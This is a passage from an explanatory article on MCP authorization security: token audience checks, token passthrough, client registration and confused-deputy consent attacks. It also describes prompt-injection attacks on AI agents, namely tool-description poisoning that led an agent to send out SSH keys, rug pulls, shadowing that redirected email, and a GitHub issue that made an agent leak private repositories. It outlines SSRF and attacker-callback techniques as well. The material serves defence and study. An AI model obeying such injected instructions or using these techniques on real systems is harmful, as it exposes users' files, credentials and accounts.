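The signature is genuine because the real authorization server made it. B trusts the issuer (`iss`), the scope is right and the expiry time (`exp`) hasn't passed. Only the audience (`aud`) is wrong, because it contains A's address instead of B's. If B checks the audience, it rejects the request with status 401, and A's operator can't use the token there. If B doesn't check it, B accepts the token and returns the files. B's logs would show an ordinary request with a valid token.

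Jones and colleagues note that this attack is also possible in plain OAuth, but clients that configure themselves at run time make it somewhat more likely. A developer setting up a calendar app by hand would probably wonder why it needs permission to read files, but an agent's client requests whatever scope the refusal lists.

B's check depends on an earlier one by the client. A's operator could put B's address in the `resource` field of A's metadata. A client that doesn't check the field might copy that address into its token request, receive a token whose audience is B, and send the token to A. A's operator could then present it to B, which would accept it without breaking any rule. To prevent this, the client compares the `resource` value with the address it called and discards the metadata document if they differ.

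The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires a tool server to reject any token that it can't confirm is meant for it, even if the authorization server ignores the `resource` parameter. Some identity providers fill the audience field with something other than a web address. According to the Model Context Protocol's Python documentation, Auth0 uses an API identifier and Entra uses an application ID, so the developer has to write a check for those values.

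That documentation also shows that the Python kit makes a firm rule optional. Its built-in audience check, `validate_token_resource`, is off unless the developer turns it on. Leaving it unset produces a warning, and version 3.0 of the kit will turn it on by default. The kit is cautious because an automatic comparison of addresses would reject valid tokens from Auth0 or Entra. But a developer who overlooks the warning and doesn't write a check ends up with a server in B's position. It isn't clear from the documentation how many servers are in this position.

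Audience checks also don't help when somebody steals a token that was issued for B, for example from B's logs or the client's storage. MCP's main protection against this is to keep access tokens short-lived. RFC 9728 has fields that let a service announce support for tokens tied to a key or certificate that the client holds. A thief couldn't use such a token without also stealing the key. However, MCP's core rules call for ordinary bearer tokens.

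### Why a tool server may not pass a token on

Many tool servers relay requests to another service. For example, a small company might run a tool server that sends mail through a large provider's API. In the easiest design, the client would get a token for the mail API and give it to the tool server, which would forward it with each request. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) forbids this practice, which its *Security Best Practices* calls token passthrough.

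To reach the mail API, a tool server that follows the rules acts as an OAuth client and gets a separate token from the mail provider's authorization server. The two tokens have different audiences, and neither works in place of the other.

The ban exists partly because passthrough requires the tool server to accept a token issued for another service, which means giving up the audience check. Anyone with a stolen mail token could then use the tool server to access the victim's mail. If several services accept the same token without checking its audience, an attacker who breaks into one of them can use the token at the others.

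Passthrough also makes it harder to reconstruct what happened. If the tool server can't read the token, it can't tell its clients apart. The mail provider's logs may attribute requests to another source even though the tool server sent them. Limits on how often a client may call or what it may send can fail if they depend on identifying the caller. The mail API may also accept a forwarded token on the assumption that the tool server has already checked it, which is another case of the confused deputy.

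The Model Context Protocol also argues that a tool server that only forwards requests today may need its own access rules later, and that its developer can add them more easily if the server has had its own tokens from the start.

These are good reasons for the ban, but it means the tool server has to obtain and store a mail token for every user, so an attacker who breaks into it may find all of those tokens at once. The user may also have to approve two requests, one for the tool server and another for the mail provider. Under the June revision, tool servers no longer have to issue tokens, but a tool server that calls someone else's API still has to track which upstream token belongs to which user, much as it did under the March rules.

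### Who writes the metadata

Because authorization is optional in MCP, a tool server that accepts every request without a token still conforms to the protocol.

If a tool server uses authorization, its operator writes the protected resource metadata. The client fetches this document over an encrypted connection and checks the host's certificate, which shows that the document came from `files.example.com` and that nobody changed it on the way. Comparing the `resource` values shows that the document is about the server the client called. Neither check is evidence that the operator of `files.example.com` is honest. The `authorization_servers` field lists the authorization servers that the tool server trusts, but the client still has to decide whether to trust them too.

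Jones and colleagues place how a client securely chooses an authorization server outside the scope of RFC 9728 and assume that the client has some way to do it. They warn that if the client chooses badly, an attacker may be able to sit between the client and a genuine authorization server without either one detecting it.

An attacker who runs a tool server can have it name an authorization server that the attacker also runs. When the client sends the user there, the attacker starts a parallel sign-in at the genuine `login.example.net` and relays the messages in both directions. PKCE doesn't help if the client sends both the authorization code and the verifier to the attacker's token endpoint. The audience check may not help either, because the attacker writes the request to the genuine authorization server and can name the file store as the resource.

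The user is often the last person who could notice the deception. The phishing section of RFC 9728 covers malicious or compromised services that trick users into revealing a password or granting access. It recommends that clients display the authorization server's domain name and check the domain's reputation. It also recommends password managers and authenticators tied to a particular site, which won't work on a lookalike page at another address. Jones and colleagues say these measures reduce the risk but don't eliminate it. They help little in the example of servers A and B, because the sign-in page is genuine.

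The operator of a hostile tool server can also supply addresses that the client will open. This allows server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a program to send requests to places that the attacker can't reach directly. If the client runs in a company's data center, the metadata address in the header could be `http://169.254.169.254/`, where the large cloud providers give a machine its own credentials. The reply might then leak to the attacker in an error message. The Model Context Protocol advises clients to require HTTPS, block private network addresses and apply the same checks to every redirect. Checking an address once may not be enough, because the owner of a domain can point it to a harmless machine during the check and to an internal one a moment later.

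The sign-in address can itself be dangerous. If it begins with `javascript:` and the client passes it to the browser's function for opening windows, the attacker's code runs inside the client. A client that opens addresses through a command shell could run commands the attacker has hidden in the address. MCP therefore requires clients to reject any address that isn't `http` or `https`, and to open accepted addresses without a shell.

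RFC 9728 includes two optional ways to check a tool server's claims. In one, an authorization server can publish a list of the services it works with, and the client can compare that list with the tool server's metadata. If `login.example.net` published such a list and server A wasn't on it, the client would have reason to stop before the user saw a sign-in page. The comparison doesn't catch an attacker who runs both servers, since each will list the other.

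The metadata can also include a copy of its contents signed by another organization that vouches for them. A client that supports signatures must prefer the signed values to the unsigned ones, and it can decide whether to trust them based on who signed them. Clients don't have to support signatures, though, and Jones and colleagues don't specify how a client should decide which signers to trust.

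## Tool descriptions as a channel for attack, from April 2025

In April 2025, a security company showed that the operator of a tool server can steer an agent through a tool's description without misusing a token. The server sends the description to a connected client, and the model uses it to choose its actions. The checks introduced in June 2025 determine which server can use a token, but they don't cover the text that a server sends.

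### What a tool server returns

Once the client has a token for the file store, it sends a `tools/list` request. Under the July 2026 rules, the reply might look like this.

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 2,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "tools": [
      {
        "name": "read_file",
        "description": "Read a file and return its contents",
        "inputSchema": {
          "type": "object",
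          "properties": {
            "path": {
              "type": "string",
              "description": "Path such as reports/june.csv"
            }
          },
          "required": ["path"]
        },
        "annotations": {
          "readOnlyHint": true,
          "openWorldHint": false
        }
      }
    ],
    "ttlMs": 300000,
    "cacheScope": "private"
  }
}
```

Besides the tool's main `description`, the `inputSchema` can describe each input for the model. The client may keep the list for 300,000 milliseconds, or five minutes, before it asks again. The value `private` means the client must not reuse the list with a different access token.

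The client then makes the listed tools available to the model, as *MCPSecBench* (2025) explains. Applications commonly do this by putting the tool definitions into the prompt with the user's request. The model can therefore read a tool's description and act on it without calling the tool.

The `annotations` field is mainly for the client. The Model Context Protocol schema defines four hints about a tool's behavior:

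| Hint | Meaning if true | Default | Possible use by a client |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool changes nothing | false | Skip the confirmation dialog |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may delete or overwrite data | true | Warn the user first |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call has no further effect | false | Retry after a failure |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside systems or people | true | Check the output for untrusted text |

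The defaults are the worst case, so a client should treat a tool without annotations as one that may delete data and bring in text from untrusted sources.

### Why clients can't rely on annotations

A dishonest developer can mark a tool as read-only even if it deletes the user's files. A client that skips confirmation for read-only tools would then run the deletion without asking the user. If an honest developer forgets to mark a read-only tool, the user only sees an unnecessary confirmation dialog.

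A March post by the Model Context Protocol project (2026) recounts how reviewers argued about this before the hints appeared a year earlier. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked what a client could do with a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer wanted clients to ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, including the display title. The project compromised by making all annotations hints, which clients must treat as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. Each client decides how much weight to give them.

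According to the post, most clients trust any installed server and treat a company's internal server the same as one that someone found on the internet. The post also reports that no client showed annotations in its approval prompts, so users couldn't judge the hints for themselves.

The March 2025 revision likewise states that clients should consider descriptions of tool behavior untrusted unless they come from a trusted server (copy hosted by Glama, 2025). This rule is harder to follow for the `description` field than for the hints. A client can ignore `readOnlyHint` and ask the user anyway, but if it withholds the description, the model may lack the information it needs to use the tool.

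### Instructions hidden in a description

In tool poisoning, an attacker puts malicious instructions for the model in a tool's description. The term comes from *MCP Security Notification* (1 April 2025) by Invariant Labs, a Zurich company that researches and sells security software for agents.

In its first experiment, the company connected the code editor Cursor to a tool server with a tool for adding two numbers. The tool had an extra text input, and the tool's description contained instructions for the model to read files on the user's machine and put their contents in that input. The files included Cursor's MCP configuration, which often holds the keys for other servers, and an SSH private key, which lets its holder log in to remote computers. Cursor's agent followed the instructions and sent the contents of both files to the server.

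The tool server had no access to the user's files, but the agent did, and it sent their contents out in an ordinary tool call. Checking an access token's scope and audience wouldn't have prevented this, because the attacker didn't present a token to another service.

Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but the dialog showed a summary of the tool. Even its expanded view left out the part of the input that contained the SSH key. The user could approve what looked like addition without seeing the files the agent was about to send.

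The experiment shows that the attack can work, but not how often. Invariant Labs also overstated the protocol's fault by claiming that MCP's security model assumes tool descriptions are trustworthy, since the 26 March revision had already advised against assuming this. Its criticism of the software was better founded, because many clients passed descriptions straight to the model without showing them to the user, so the advice had little effect.

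### Descriptions that change after approval

Some clients ask the user to approve a server's tools when installing it. Invariant Labs pointed out that the server's operator can change a tool's description afterwards, an attack it called a rug pull. For example, an operator could offer a harmless calendar tool for months and add malicious instructions once enough people were using it. The company compared this to software package indexes, where an attacker can publish a harmless package and later release a malicious version.

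Such a change is especially easy with a remote server, because the operator edits the text on their own machine and the user has no update to install or refuse.

MCP allows tool lists to change for good reasons, such as new features. A server may also show more tools to a client whose token carries more scopes. The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) recommends that servers supporting change notices send one to subscribed clients when their list changes, but a hostile operator can choose not to. The client will still receive the new text the next time it fetches the list. However, the rules for tools don't require it to compare the new text with the old or to ask for approval again.

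### One server's description and another server's tool

MCP keeps the calendar server and the file store separate, but their tool descriptions usually end up in the same model's context, where the text from one can affect how the model uses the other.

Invariant Labs tested this in a second experiment, connecting Cursor to a trusted server with a tool for sending email and a malicious server that again had a tool for adding numbers. The malicious tool's description contained a false rule about who should receive email from the trusted server. When the user asked the agent to email a particular person, the agent sent the email to the attacker instead. The agent's log showed the changed recipient only in the inputs of the tool call.

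The company called this shadowing. The agent never has to call the malicious tool, so a user who checks which tools the agent used will find only the trusted one. The mail server receives a well-formed request with a valid token and cannot detect that the user named a different recipient. If the operator of the calendar server adds the false rule after approval, a careful check at installation won't catch it.

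Two servers may both offer a tool called `search`, so the Model Context Protocol recommends that clients tell such tools apart, for instance by adding a server identifier to each name. The identifier shouldn't be the name the server gives itself, because the protocol doesn't verify that name and two servers may choose the same one. Unique names help the client route a call to the right server, but they don't prevent shadowing, because a malicious description can refer to another server's tool by its unique name.

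### Instructions in what a tool returns

An attacker can target an agent without controlling a tool server if a legitimate server returns text that the attacker wrote. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated this on 26 May with the official tool server of GitHub, a site where programmers store projects in public and private repositories. Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository.

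The attack ran as follows:

1. The attacker filed an issue in the user's public repository and included instructions for an agent.
2. The user asked the agent to look at the repository's open issues.
3. The agent called a tool to fetch the issues, and the server returned the attacker's text with the rest.
4. The model followed the instructions and used the server to read the user's private repositories.
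5. The agent put what it had found into a pull request, a proposed change to a project, in the public repository. Anyone could then read it.

Invariant Labs ran the test in the Claude Desktop application with Claude 4 Opus, then a recent model, using an account it had set up for the purpose. The pull request revealed the names of private repositories, the account owner's salary and a plan to move to South America.

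The server worked as intended. Heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent could reach the private data because the server acted through the user's own account. That account had permission to read the issues, read the private repositories and open the pull request. Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub couldn't fix the problem by changing the server alone.

Claude Desktop asks users to confirm each tool call by default, so an attentive user could have stopped the leak. According to DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP*, the researchers suspected that many users choose "always allow" instead. They gave no figures, but that choice would be understandable after a long series of harmless calls.

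In *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison (2025) identified three conditions that together make this kind of theft possible: the agent can reach private data, it reads text that an attacker may have written, and it can send information out. He calls the combination the "lethal trifecta". GitHub's server met all three by itself. In other cases, the user creates the combination by connecting several servers. For example, the file store could hold private reports, a calendar could contain a stranger's invitation, and the mail service could send the reports out.

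The risk therefore depends on the whole session, as the Model Context Protocol project points out in its post on annotations, so a tool that searches email isn't safe or dangerous on its own. An accurate `openWorldHint` could warn a client that a tool's output may contain text from strangers, but it doesn't help the model resist instructions in that text. The hint can also be technically correct but misleading. The developer of the file store might reasonably describe it as a closed system, even though one of the reports in it came from an outsider.

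The project suggests that better annotations could let a client treat a session as tainted after a tool returns untrusted content, and require the user's approval for later actions. As of March 2026, five proposals for new annotations or related features were open, including one from GitHub and OpenAI on trust and sensitivity. These proposals would still depend on honest labels from servers.

Under the Model Context Protocol, clients should also validate tool results before passing them to the model. This can catch a result in the wrong format, such as text where the client expected a number. Validation alone wouldn't have caught the GitHub attack, because an issue is supposed to contain free text.

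Invariant Labs advised users to give agents access only to the repositories they need. It also published a rule for its security product to limit an agent to one repository per session. The rule would have stopped the agent from moving between the public repository and the private ones. It would also stop a user from copying code between two projects, and it wouldn't cover private data from a different server. Other designs aim to limit what an agent can do after an attacker has misled its model.

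### How common poisoned descriptions are

*Model Context Protocol (MCP) at First Glance* (Hasan, Li and colleagues, 2025) reported tool poisoning in 5.5% of MCP servers. This was about four servers, although 5.5% of the 1,899 open-source servers, the total given in the abstract, would be about 100.

The researchers checked all 583 code repositories in their dataset with SonarQube, a general program for finding flaws in source code, and found at least one ordinary security vulnerability in 7.2% of them. SonarQube doesn't look for tool poisoning, so they also used mcp-scan, a scanner from Invariant Labs that reads the tool descriptions of a running server. Running each server required installing its software and supplying its credentials, so they limited this scan to a random sample of 83 repositories. The scanner worked on 60 of them at first and on 13 more after its maintainers fixed a fault.

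The 5.5% figure matches four servers out of 73. With so few cases, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 2% to 13%. These cases are labelled "potential" tool poisoning in the detailed results, but not in the abstract. The qualification matters because an honest developer may also put instructions to the model in a description, for example to call one tool before another, and a scanner has to distinguish these from an attack.

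The scanner can also miss dangerous servers, because it reads descriptions and not source code. While setting up the sample, the researchers noticed two problems that the scanner did not flag: a server for Apple's Notes application required access to the user's whole disk, and another server had automatic approval for sensitive operations.

Public vulnerability records give little further help. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) examined 119 entries in CVE, a public catalog of known software flaws, and confirmed that 24 concerned MCP. Most of these let attackers run unwanted commands or reach forbidden files. Such catalogs mainly record programming mistakes, whereas a poisoned description is deliberate. In the 2026 version of their paper, Hasan and colleagues call for vulnerability databases to include MCP-specific problems.

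### How often the attacks succeed

A poisoned description causes harm only if the model follows it. Researchers measure how often this happens with the attack success rate, the share of test runs in which the agent does what the attacker wanted.

SkillSafe's *MCP Tool Poisoning* cites a January 2026 paper on automated attacks that reported success rates of up to 84.2% across 12 agents. The typical rate may have been much lower. The result applies to models available by January 2026, so it is weak evidence about current models, which may have had more training against such attacks but may also follow instructions more reliably, including an attacker's.

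An attack's result depends on the client as well as the model. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) describes earlier research that used malicious servers and four types of attack to test seven applications, including Claude Desktop, Cursor and Gemini CLI. Testing whole applications is useful because two that run the same model can expose users to different risks. One might show every input before a call, while the other shows only a short summary that omits a stolen file in the input.

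Even a low success rate can be serious if the agent reads the poisoned description in every session. If an attack succeeds with probability p in each session, and the sessions are independent, the chance of at least one success in n sessions is:

`P = 1 − (1 − p)^n`

If an attack succeeds in 2% of sessions, the chance that it succeeds at least once in 100 independent sessions is about 87%. Real sessions aren't fully independent, since a model that ignores a text once may ignore it again. Still, a rate that looks small in a benchmark might not be low enough to protect somebody who uses an agent every day.

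### Detecting changed descriptions

Invariant Labs recommended that clients pin tools, which means accepting only the version that the user approved. A client can do this with a hash, a short fingerprint of a longer text:

`fingerprint = SHA256(name, description, inputSchema, annotations)`

The client stores this hash for each tool when the user approves it and recomputes it whenever it fetches the list. If even one character has changed, the hashes differ, and the client can block the tool until someone reviews it. The hash has to cover the schema because an attacker could put instructions in the description of an input. The client also has to treat a new tool as a change, since its description could interfere with the tools the user has already approved.

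Pinning is a strong defense against rug pulls through descriptions, but it doesn't help if the text was malicious when the user approved it. It also doesn't check the program behind the description. For a local server, the client can also pin the version of the software package, but the operator of a remote server can replace the program without changing the description. Tool results can't be pinned because they are supposed to change.

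Harmless edits also change the hash. If a client prompts users to approve every spelling correction, they will soon approve changes without reading them.

### Signatures and registry review

The author of a tool description can also sign it. *MCP-38* (2026) cites one such proposal, ETDI. According to its title, ETDI uses "OAuth-enhanced tool definitions" and access rules to counter rug pulls and tools that imitate others.

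A signature can show who signed a description and that nobody altered it afterwards, which helps when it passes through a directory or another intermediary. For a remote server, the encrypted connection already shows that the description came from the right host. But an attacker can sign a malicious description with their own key, and the signature will be valid. Signatures on the site-wide descriptors proposed in 2026 have the same limit.

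A registry, or directory of tool servers, could review each server's tool descriptions before listing it, and reject servers that imitate well-known ones. A reviewer with time and training is more likely to notice a suspicious instruction than a user trying to finish a task. But the operator of a remote server can change the descriptions after the registry approves them.

A hostile operator could also show the reviewer a different tool list from the one users see. Since July 2026, MCP has forbidden servers to vary their tool lists between connections, according to the protocol's changelog. Lists may still depend on the caller's authorization, so an operator could recognize the reviewer's token and return harmless text. A hostile operator may also ignore the rule.

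Many tool servers also disappear within days. *Exposed by Design* (2026), a survey of tool servers on the public internet, found that 41.6% of confirmed servers were gone at the next measurement, about 72 hours later. Many may have been experiments that no registry would list, and some may have returned. Still, if a registry checked each server only once, some of its results would soon be outdated.

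### The limits of scanning

Hasan and colleagues want registries to scan servers automatically, as one of several measures to keep the MCP ecosystem safe in the long term. They found their own scans laborious to set up, but accuracy is a more serious problem.

Chen, An and colleagues (2026), in *Rethinking MCP Security*, tested scanners on a much larger collection of 64,611 unique servers, more than 37,288 of which support testing while they run. They used cooperating agents to turn public code repositories into running servers, repair failed installations and confirm that each server answered real protocol requests.

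Existing scanners classified 96.89% of the servers as risky, which is too many for the warnings to help a user choose between servers. Fewer than half of the alerts in a sample checked by hand were correct, and the scanners disagreed with one another. These results cover many kinds of security problem, so they don't give an error rate for tool poisoning and can't be used to adjust the 5.5% figure from Hasan and colleagues.

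Even a much better scanner would produce many false alarms if attacks are rare. Suppose 1% of servers are poisoned, and a scanner catches 90% of these and wrongly flags 5% of the others. Among 10,000 servers, it would correctly flag 90 and wrongly flag 495, so only about 15% of its warnings would be right. A registry could have people check all 585 flagged servers, but an individual user who sees mostly false warnings will probably start to ignore them.

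An attacker can also test malicious text against a public scanner and rewrite it until it passes. Scanning descriptions at installation doesn't cover tool results. Invariant Labs has added a mode in which its scanner sits between the client and the servers and checks messages as they pass. This covers more of the text that reaches the model, but the scanner still has to recognize an attack, and the company says many existing prompt injection detectors failed to catch the GitHub attack.

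### Showing the text to the user

Invariant Labs recommended that clients show users the full tool descriptions and mark which parts the model will see. The Model Context Protocol recommends that clients show users the inputs of a call before sending it, partly to prevent data theft, and ask them to confirm sensitive operations.

A tool call's inputs are often more useful to the user than the tool's description. In the mail experiment, a dialog that displayed the recipient's address would have let the user spot the attack without understanding how it worked. In the SSH key experiment, displaying the inputs in full would have revealed the contents of the user's files. An attacker might respond by having the model encode the data, and the user would then have to decide whether a long string of meaningless characters was suspicious.

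When a description changes, the client could highlight the new words instead of showing the whole text again. This would make the review after a failed hash check much shorter. The user would still have to judge whether the new text is a legitimate instruction, which may be difficult for someone who didn't write the tool.

Confirmation prompts also interrupt agents that many people use to finish tasks without supervision. The Model Context Protocol project reports that developers of autonomous agents regard these prompts as friction and prefer to run the agent in a sandbox, an isolated environment that restricts what it can reach. To guarantee that a tool can't send data out, the project recommends sandboxing or network controls, because these work even if the model relies on a false description.

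## How an unknown client registers, November 2025 to May 2026

An authorization server has to decide how far to trust an unfamiliar client, just as a client does with an unfamiliar tool server. In the file store example, the client gave the identifier `agent-app` when it opened the sign-in page. The authorization server needs a record for that identifier, with at least a name to show the user and a list of callbacks. A callback, or redirect URI, is the address to which the browser returns with the authorization code. If an attacker gets their own address onto the list, the authorization server will send the code to the attacker.

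Since November 2025, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) has had three ways to create this record. Its *Client Registration* (2026) sets the order in which a client should try them. The client first uses an identifier that somebody obtained for it in advance. If it has none, it uses a client ID metadata document, and if the authorization server doesn't support those, it registers itself dynamically. As a last resort, it asks the user to enter the details.

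### Registration in advance

Pre-registration is the manual process that ordinary apps use. The developer enters the app's name and callback URLs on the service's website and receives a client identifier and sometimes a secret. Users can also register a client themselves and paste the identifier into the agent app.

Services normally review client registrations because whoever runs a client ends up holding its users' access tokens, as hi120ki explains in a personal blog post, *Weaponize the MCP*. The review gives the service a chance to refuse the client.

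Pre-registration works well between companies that already know each other, but the work grows quickly. If m clients each have to reach n authorization servers, people have to complete

`m × n`

registrations. For 20 clients and 1,000 authorization servers, that is 20,000. Carleton and Parecki (2025), in *Enable URL-based Client Registration using OAuth Client ID Metadata Documents*, point out that a developer can't register with a service that doesn't exist yet when the client ships. Leaving the task to users means that they have to manage credentials by hand.

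### Dynamic client registration

With dynamic client registration, the client sends its details to an address listed in the authorization server's metadata and gets an identifier back. For the file store, the request might look like the one below, which adds an `application_type` field to a sample from Lynskey's *Model Context Protocol Series*.

```http
POST /register HTTP/1.1
Host: login.example.net
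Content-Type: application/json

{
  "client_name": "Example Agent",
  "redirect_uris": ["http://localhost:8765/callback"],
  "application_type": "native",
  "grant_types": ["authorization_code"],
  "response_types": ["code"],
  "token_endpoint_auth_method": "none"
}
```

The important part of the reply is one line:

```json
{ "client_id": "5f8a-27c1" }
```

The value `none` means the client has no secret of its own. A desktop program can't keep one because anyone who installs the program can extract it. The July 2026 revision of MCP made `application_type` required. OpenID Connect treats a client that omits this field as a web application, so the authorization server may reject a callback on the user's machine.

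Everything in the request is the sender's own claim. An attacker can send the same request with the same name and a callback at `https://attacker.example/cb`, and the authorization server will have two records for "Example Agent" with no way to tell which is genuine. Carleton and Parecki also note that the server has to store a growing number of registrations and decide when to delete old ones. If every installation of an application registers separately, the operator can't easily allow or block the application as a whole.

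Many companies never offered dynamic registration. Obsidian Security's *When MCP Meets OAuth* reports that only 27 of the 660 authorization servers the company tested, or 4%, supported it. Obsidian attributes this to fear of spam, phishing and denial-of-service attacks. hi120ki reports that some services, including Atlassian and Notion, did open registration to everyone for MCP.

### A client identifier that is a web address

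A client ID metadata document contains much the same details, but the client's developer publishes it on a website. The document's URL is the client's identifier. This example adapts one from the Model Context Protocol.

```json
{
  "client_id": "https://agent.example.com/oauth/client.json",
  "client_name": "Example Agent",
  "client_uri": "https://agent.example.com",
  "redirect_uris": [
    "http://127.0.0.1:8765/callback",
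    "http://localhost:8765/callback"
  ],
  "grant_types": ["authorization_code"],
  "response_types": ["code"],
  "token_endpoint_auth_method": "none"
}
```

The sign-in then runs as follows:

1. The client reads the authorization server's metadata and finds the entry `"client_id_metadata_document_supported": true`.
2. It opens the user's browser at the sign-in page. The `client_id` in the link is the document's address, and the `redirect_uri` is one of the callbacks in the document.
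3. The authorization server signs the user in and fetches the document.
4. It checks that the `client_id` inside the document is identical to the address it fetched, and that the callback in the link is on the document's list. It may also apply its own policy about which domains to accept.
5. It shows a consent page with the client's name. MCP also requires it to show the hostname of the callback.
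6. If the user agrees, the authorization server sends the code to the callback, and the rest of the flow is unchanged.

If the authorization server can't fetch the document or finds it invalid, it must not send the browser back to the client, because it has no trustworthy callback URL.

*OAuth Client ID Metadata Document* (Parecki and Smith, 2026), the latest draft of the format, requires strict comparison of identifiers, so `https://example.com/client` and `https://example.com:443/client` are different clients even though both addresses lead to the same place. The draft also prohibits shared secrets in the metadata document because anyone can read it. A client that runs on a web server can publish a public key there and sign its token requests with the matching private key, so a thief who copies the identifier can't redeem authorization codes. Desktop clients usually declare `none` as their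 authentication method, as in the example. The draft's preferred field now lists several authentication methods, because a single value may not suit every authorization server.

### Why MCP changed its preference

Carleton and Parecki submitted their proposal to the MCP project in July 2025. The IETF's OAuth working group adopted the format on 8 October, according to the version history of its *OAuth Client ID Metadata Document* (2025). The November revision of MCP recommended that clients and authorization servers support metadata documents, and it made dynamic registration optional.

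The main attraction is that each client needs one document instead of one registration per authorization server. The server can fetch the document when a user arrives and has no permanent register to clean up. The client's identifier is the same on every server, so an operator can accept any client with an HTTPS address or only those from a short list of domains. Carleton and Parecki considered three alternatives. Signed statements about the client's software would have required more setup, client certificates would have required an authority that everybody trusts, and compulsory pre-registration would have kept the existing burden on developers and users.

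The July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol went further and deprecated dynamic registration, so new software shouldn't adopt it. Deprecated features stay in the protocol for at least twelve months, and a draft of the next revision still includes dynamic registration for older authorization servers.

Those servers may be around for some time. After the November revision, Obsidian Security tested 78 MCP authorization servers and found that three supported metadata documents. The sample is small and the revision was recent, so the result is weak evidence of adoption in late 2026. The format is still a draft. Carleton and Parecki conceded that it might change, and that a third registration method could make MCP's already difficult authorization rules harder to implement.

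### What control of a domain proves

Parecki (2025) summarizes the idea as "If you trust example.com, you trust the client." Fetching the document over HTTPS confirms to the authorization server that whoever controls `agent.example.com` published the document and listed the callbacks in it. If an attacker uses the genuine identifier with a callback at `attacker.example`, the request fails the check in step 4. Under dynamic registration, the attacker could have created a new record instead.

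But the attacker can buy a similar domain and publish a document there with the same name and logo. That document is valid, and the consent page will show a familiar name. Parecki and Smith therefore recommend also showing the client identifier's hostname. They suggest that an authorization server could display names and logos only for reviewed clients, warn about recently registered domains, or show an extra warning to the first 100 people who authorize a client. A server that displays a logo has to store its own copy, because the client could otherwise replace the image after a moderator approved it.

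The document shows only that the owner of its domain chose the callbacks listed in it. Those callbacks can be on another domain unless the authorization server requires the domains to match. Carleton and Parecki go further and claim that servers can trust that the client controls the callbacks.

If a developer lets a client's domain expire and a stranger buys it, the stranger takes over the client's identity at every authorization server that accepted the client. An authorization server may respond to a changed key or callback by asking for consent again or revoking old tokens, but Parecki and Smith leave that decision to each operator.

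### Callbacks to the user's own machine

Control of a domain is the weakest proof of identity for desktop clients, because they receive the authorization code at `localhost`, where any program on the user's machine can listen for connections.

Suppose a hostile program starts a sign-in with a genuine client's identifier, `https://agent.example.com/oauth/client.json`, and a `localhost` callback on which the program is listening. The authorization server fetches the genuine document, and the user sees the client's name and approves. The browser then delivers the authorization code to the hostile program. PKCE doesn't prevent this, because the hostile program generated the verifier.

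The program may not need the genuine client's port number. Authorization servers normally compare callbacks exactly, but OAuth's security rules exempt the port in local callbacks because a desktop program often has to take whichever port is free.

Dynamic registration has the same weakness. The Model Context Protocol recommends an additional warning for clients that have only `localhost` callbacks. The authorization page must also show the callback's hostname, but this helps less here because the page shows `localhost` for both honest and hostile clients. An attacker first needs a program on the user's machine. Such a program could already read any API keys in the user's configuration files, but impersonating a client could also give it access to services for which the user has stored no key.

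A developer could run a server that recognizes genuine copies of the client and signs a short-lived statement for each sign-in, perhaps after a check by the phone's operating system. Carleton and Parecki note that these checks aren't available on every platform and that a hostile program might relay its requests to the developer's signing server. They left a complete solution out of their proposal.

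### When a stranger chooses the URL

Metadata documents also put the authorization server at risk because it has to fetch an address that an unknown client supplied. An attacker could make the server request an administration page inside the company's network by giving that page's address as the client identifier. Hostile tool servers can attempt the same kind of attack, called server-side request forgery, against clients.

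Parecki and Smith forbid production authorization servers from fetching documents from private and other special-purpose network addresses. The same rule covers addresses inside the document, such as the location of a logo or a public key. The server also must not follow redirects automatically, and it should stop reading at a set size limit. They recommend 5 kilobytes. Carleton and Parecki add that the server should fetch the document only after the user has signed in, which at least forces an attacker to have an account.

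An attacker might instead use many authorization servers to flood another website with requests. Carleton and Parecki think this is unlikely to appeal to attackers, because each request uses about as much of the attacker's bandwidth as the victim's, and the authorization servers can store the result instead of fetching it again. Storing results also protects privacy, since the client's developer can see from each fetch that somebody may be signing in.

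### Tool servers that are also clients

A company whose main authorization server rejects unknown clients can still offer a tool server to every agent by using a version of the third-party flow from MCP's March 2025 revision. In this version, the tool server accepts any client and is itself a client of the main authorization server. Obsidian Security found this design common among online business services.

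Take a tool server that sends mail through a large provider. The sign-in has two stages:

1. The tool server's operator registers it with the mail provider and receives one fixed client identifier, `mail-tools`. This happens once.
2. The agent's client registers with the tool server and gets its own identifier.
3. The client opens the user's browser at the tool server's sign-in address.
4. The tool server sends the browser on to the mail provider, with the identifier `mail-tools` and a new `state` value. The provider will return this value unchanged, so the tool server can use it to look up which client is waiting.
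5. The user signs in at the provider and agrees. The provider may remember that this user has approved `mail-tools`.
6. The provider sends the browser back to the tool server, which gets a mail token and then sends a code of its own to the client's callback. The client exchanges this code for a token that works at the tool server.

However many agents use the tool server, the mail provider sees one client, so its memory of the user's consent covers all of them.

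### How consent reaches the wrong client

An attacker can exploit that memory by registering a client with the tool server, giving a callback at `attacker.example`, and sending a sign-in link to someone who already uses the server. When the victim clicks the link, the mail provider recognizes `mail-tools` and skips its consent page, and the tool server sends its authorization code to the attacker. The attacker exchanges the code for a token and can then use the victim's mail account through the tool server.

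The Model Context Protocol (MCP) guidance for the June 2025 revision already covered this kind of confused deputy attack. It lists four conditions for the attack: the tool server uses a fixed identifier with the upstream service, it lets clients register dynamically, the upstream service stores consent, and the tool server doesn't ask for separate consent for each client.

The obvious fix is for the tool server to show a consent page before it sends the browser to the provider. The page must name the client, the permissions and the callback. Obsidian found that an attacker can bypass this page by opening it in their own browser, clicking "approve", and sending the victim the address of the next step, at the mail provider. The victim's browser starts from that step, so the victim never sees the consent page.

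To stop this, the tool server has to check that the sign-in finishes in the same browser where somebody approved the client. It can set a cookie after the approval and tie the `state` value to it. When the victim's browser returns from the provider without the cookie, the tool server refuses to issue a code. The server must not set the cookie before the approval, because if it did so when the consent page loaded, an attacker's link could put the cookie in the victim's browser without any approval.

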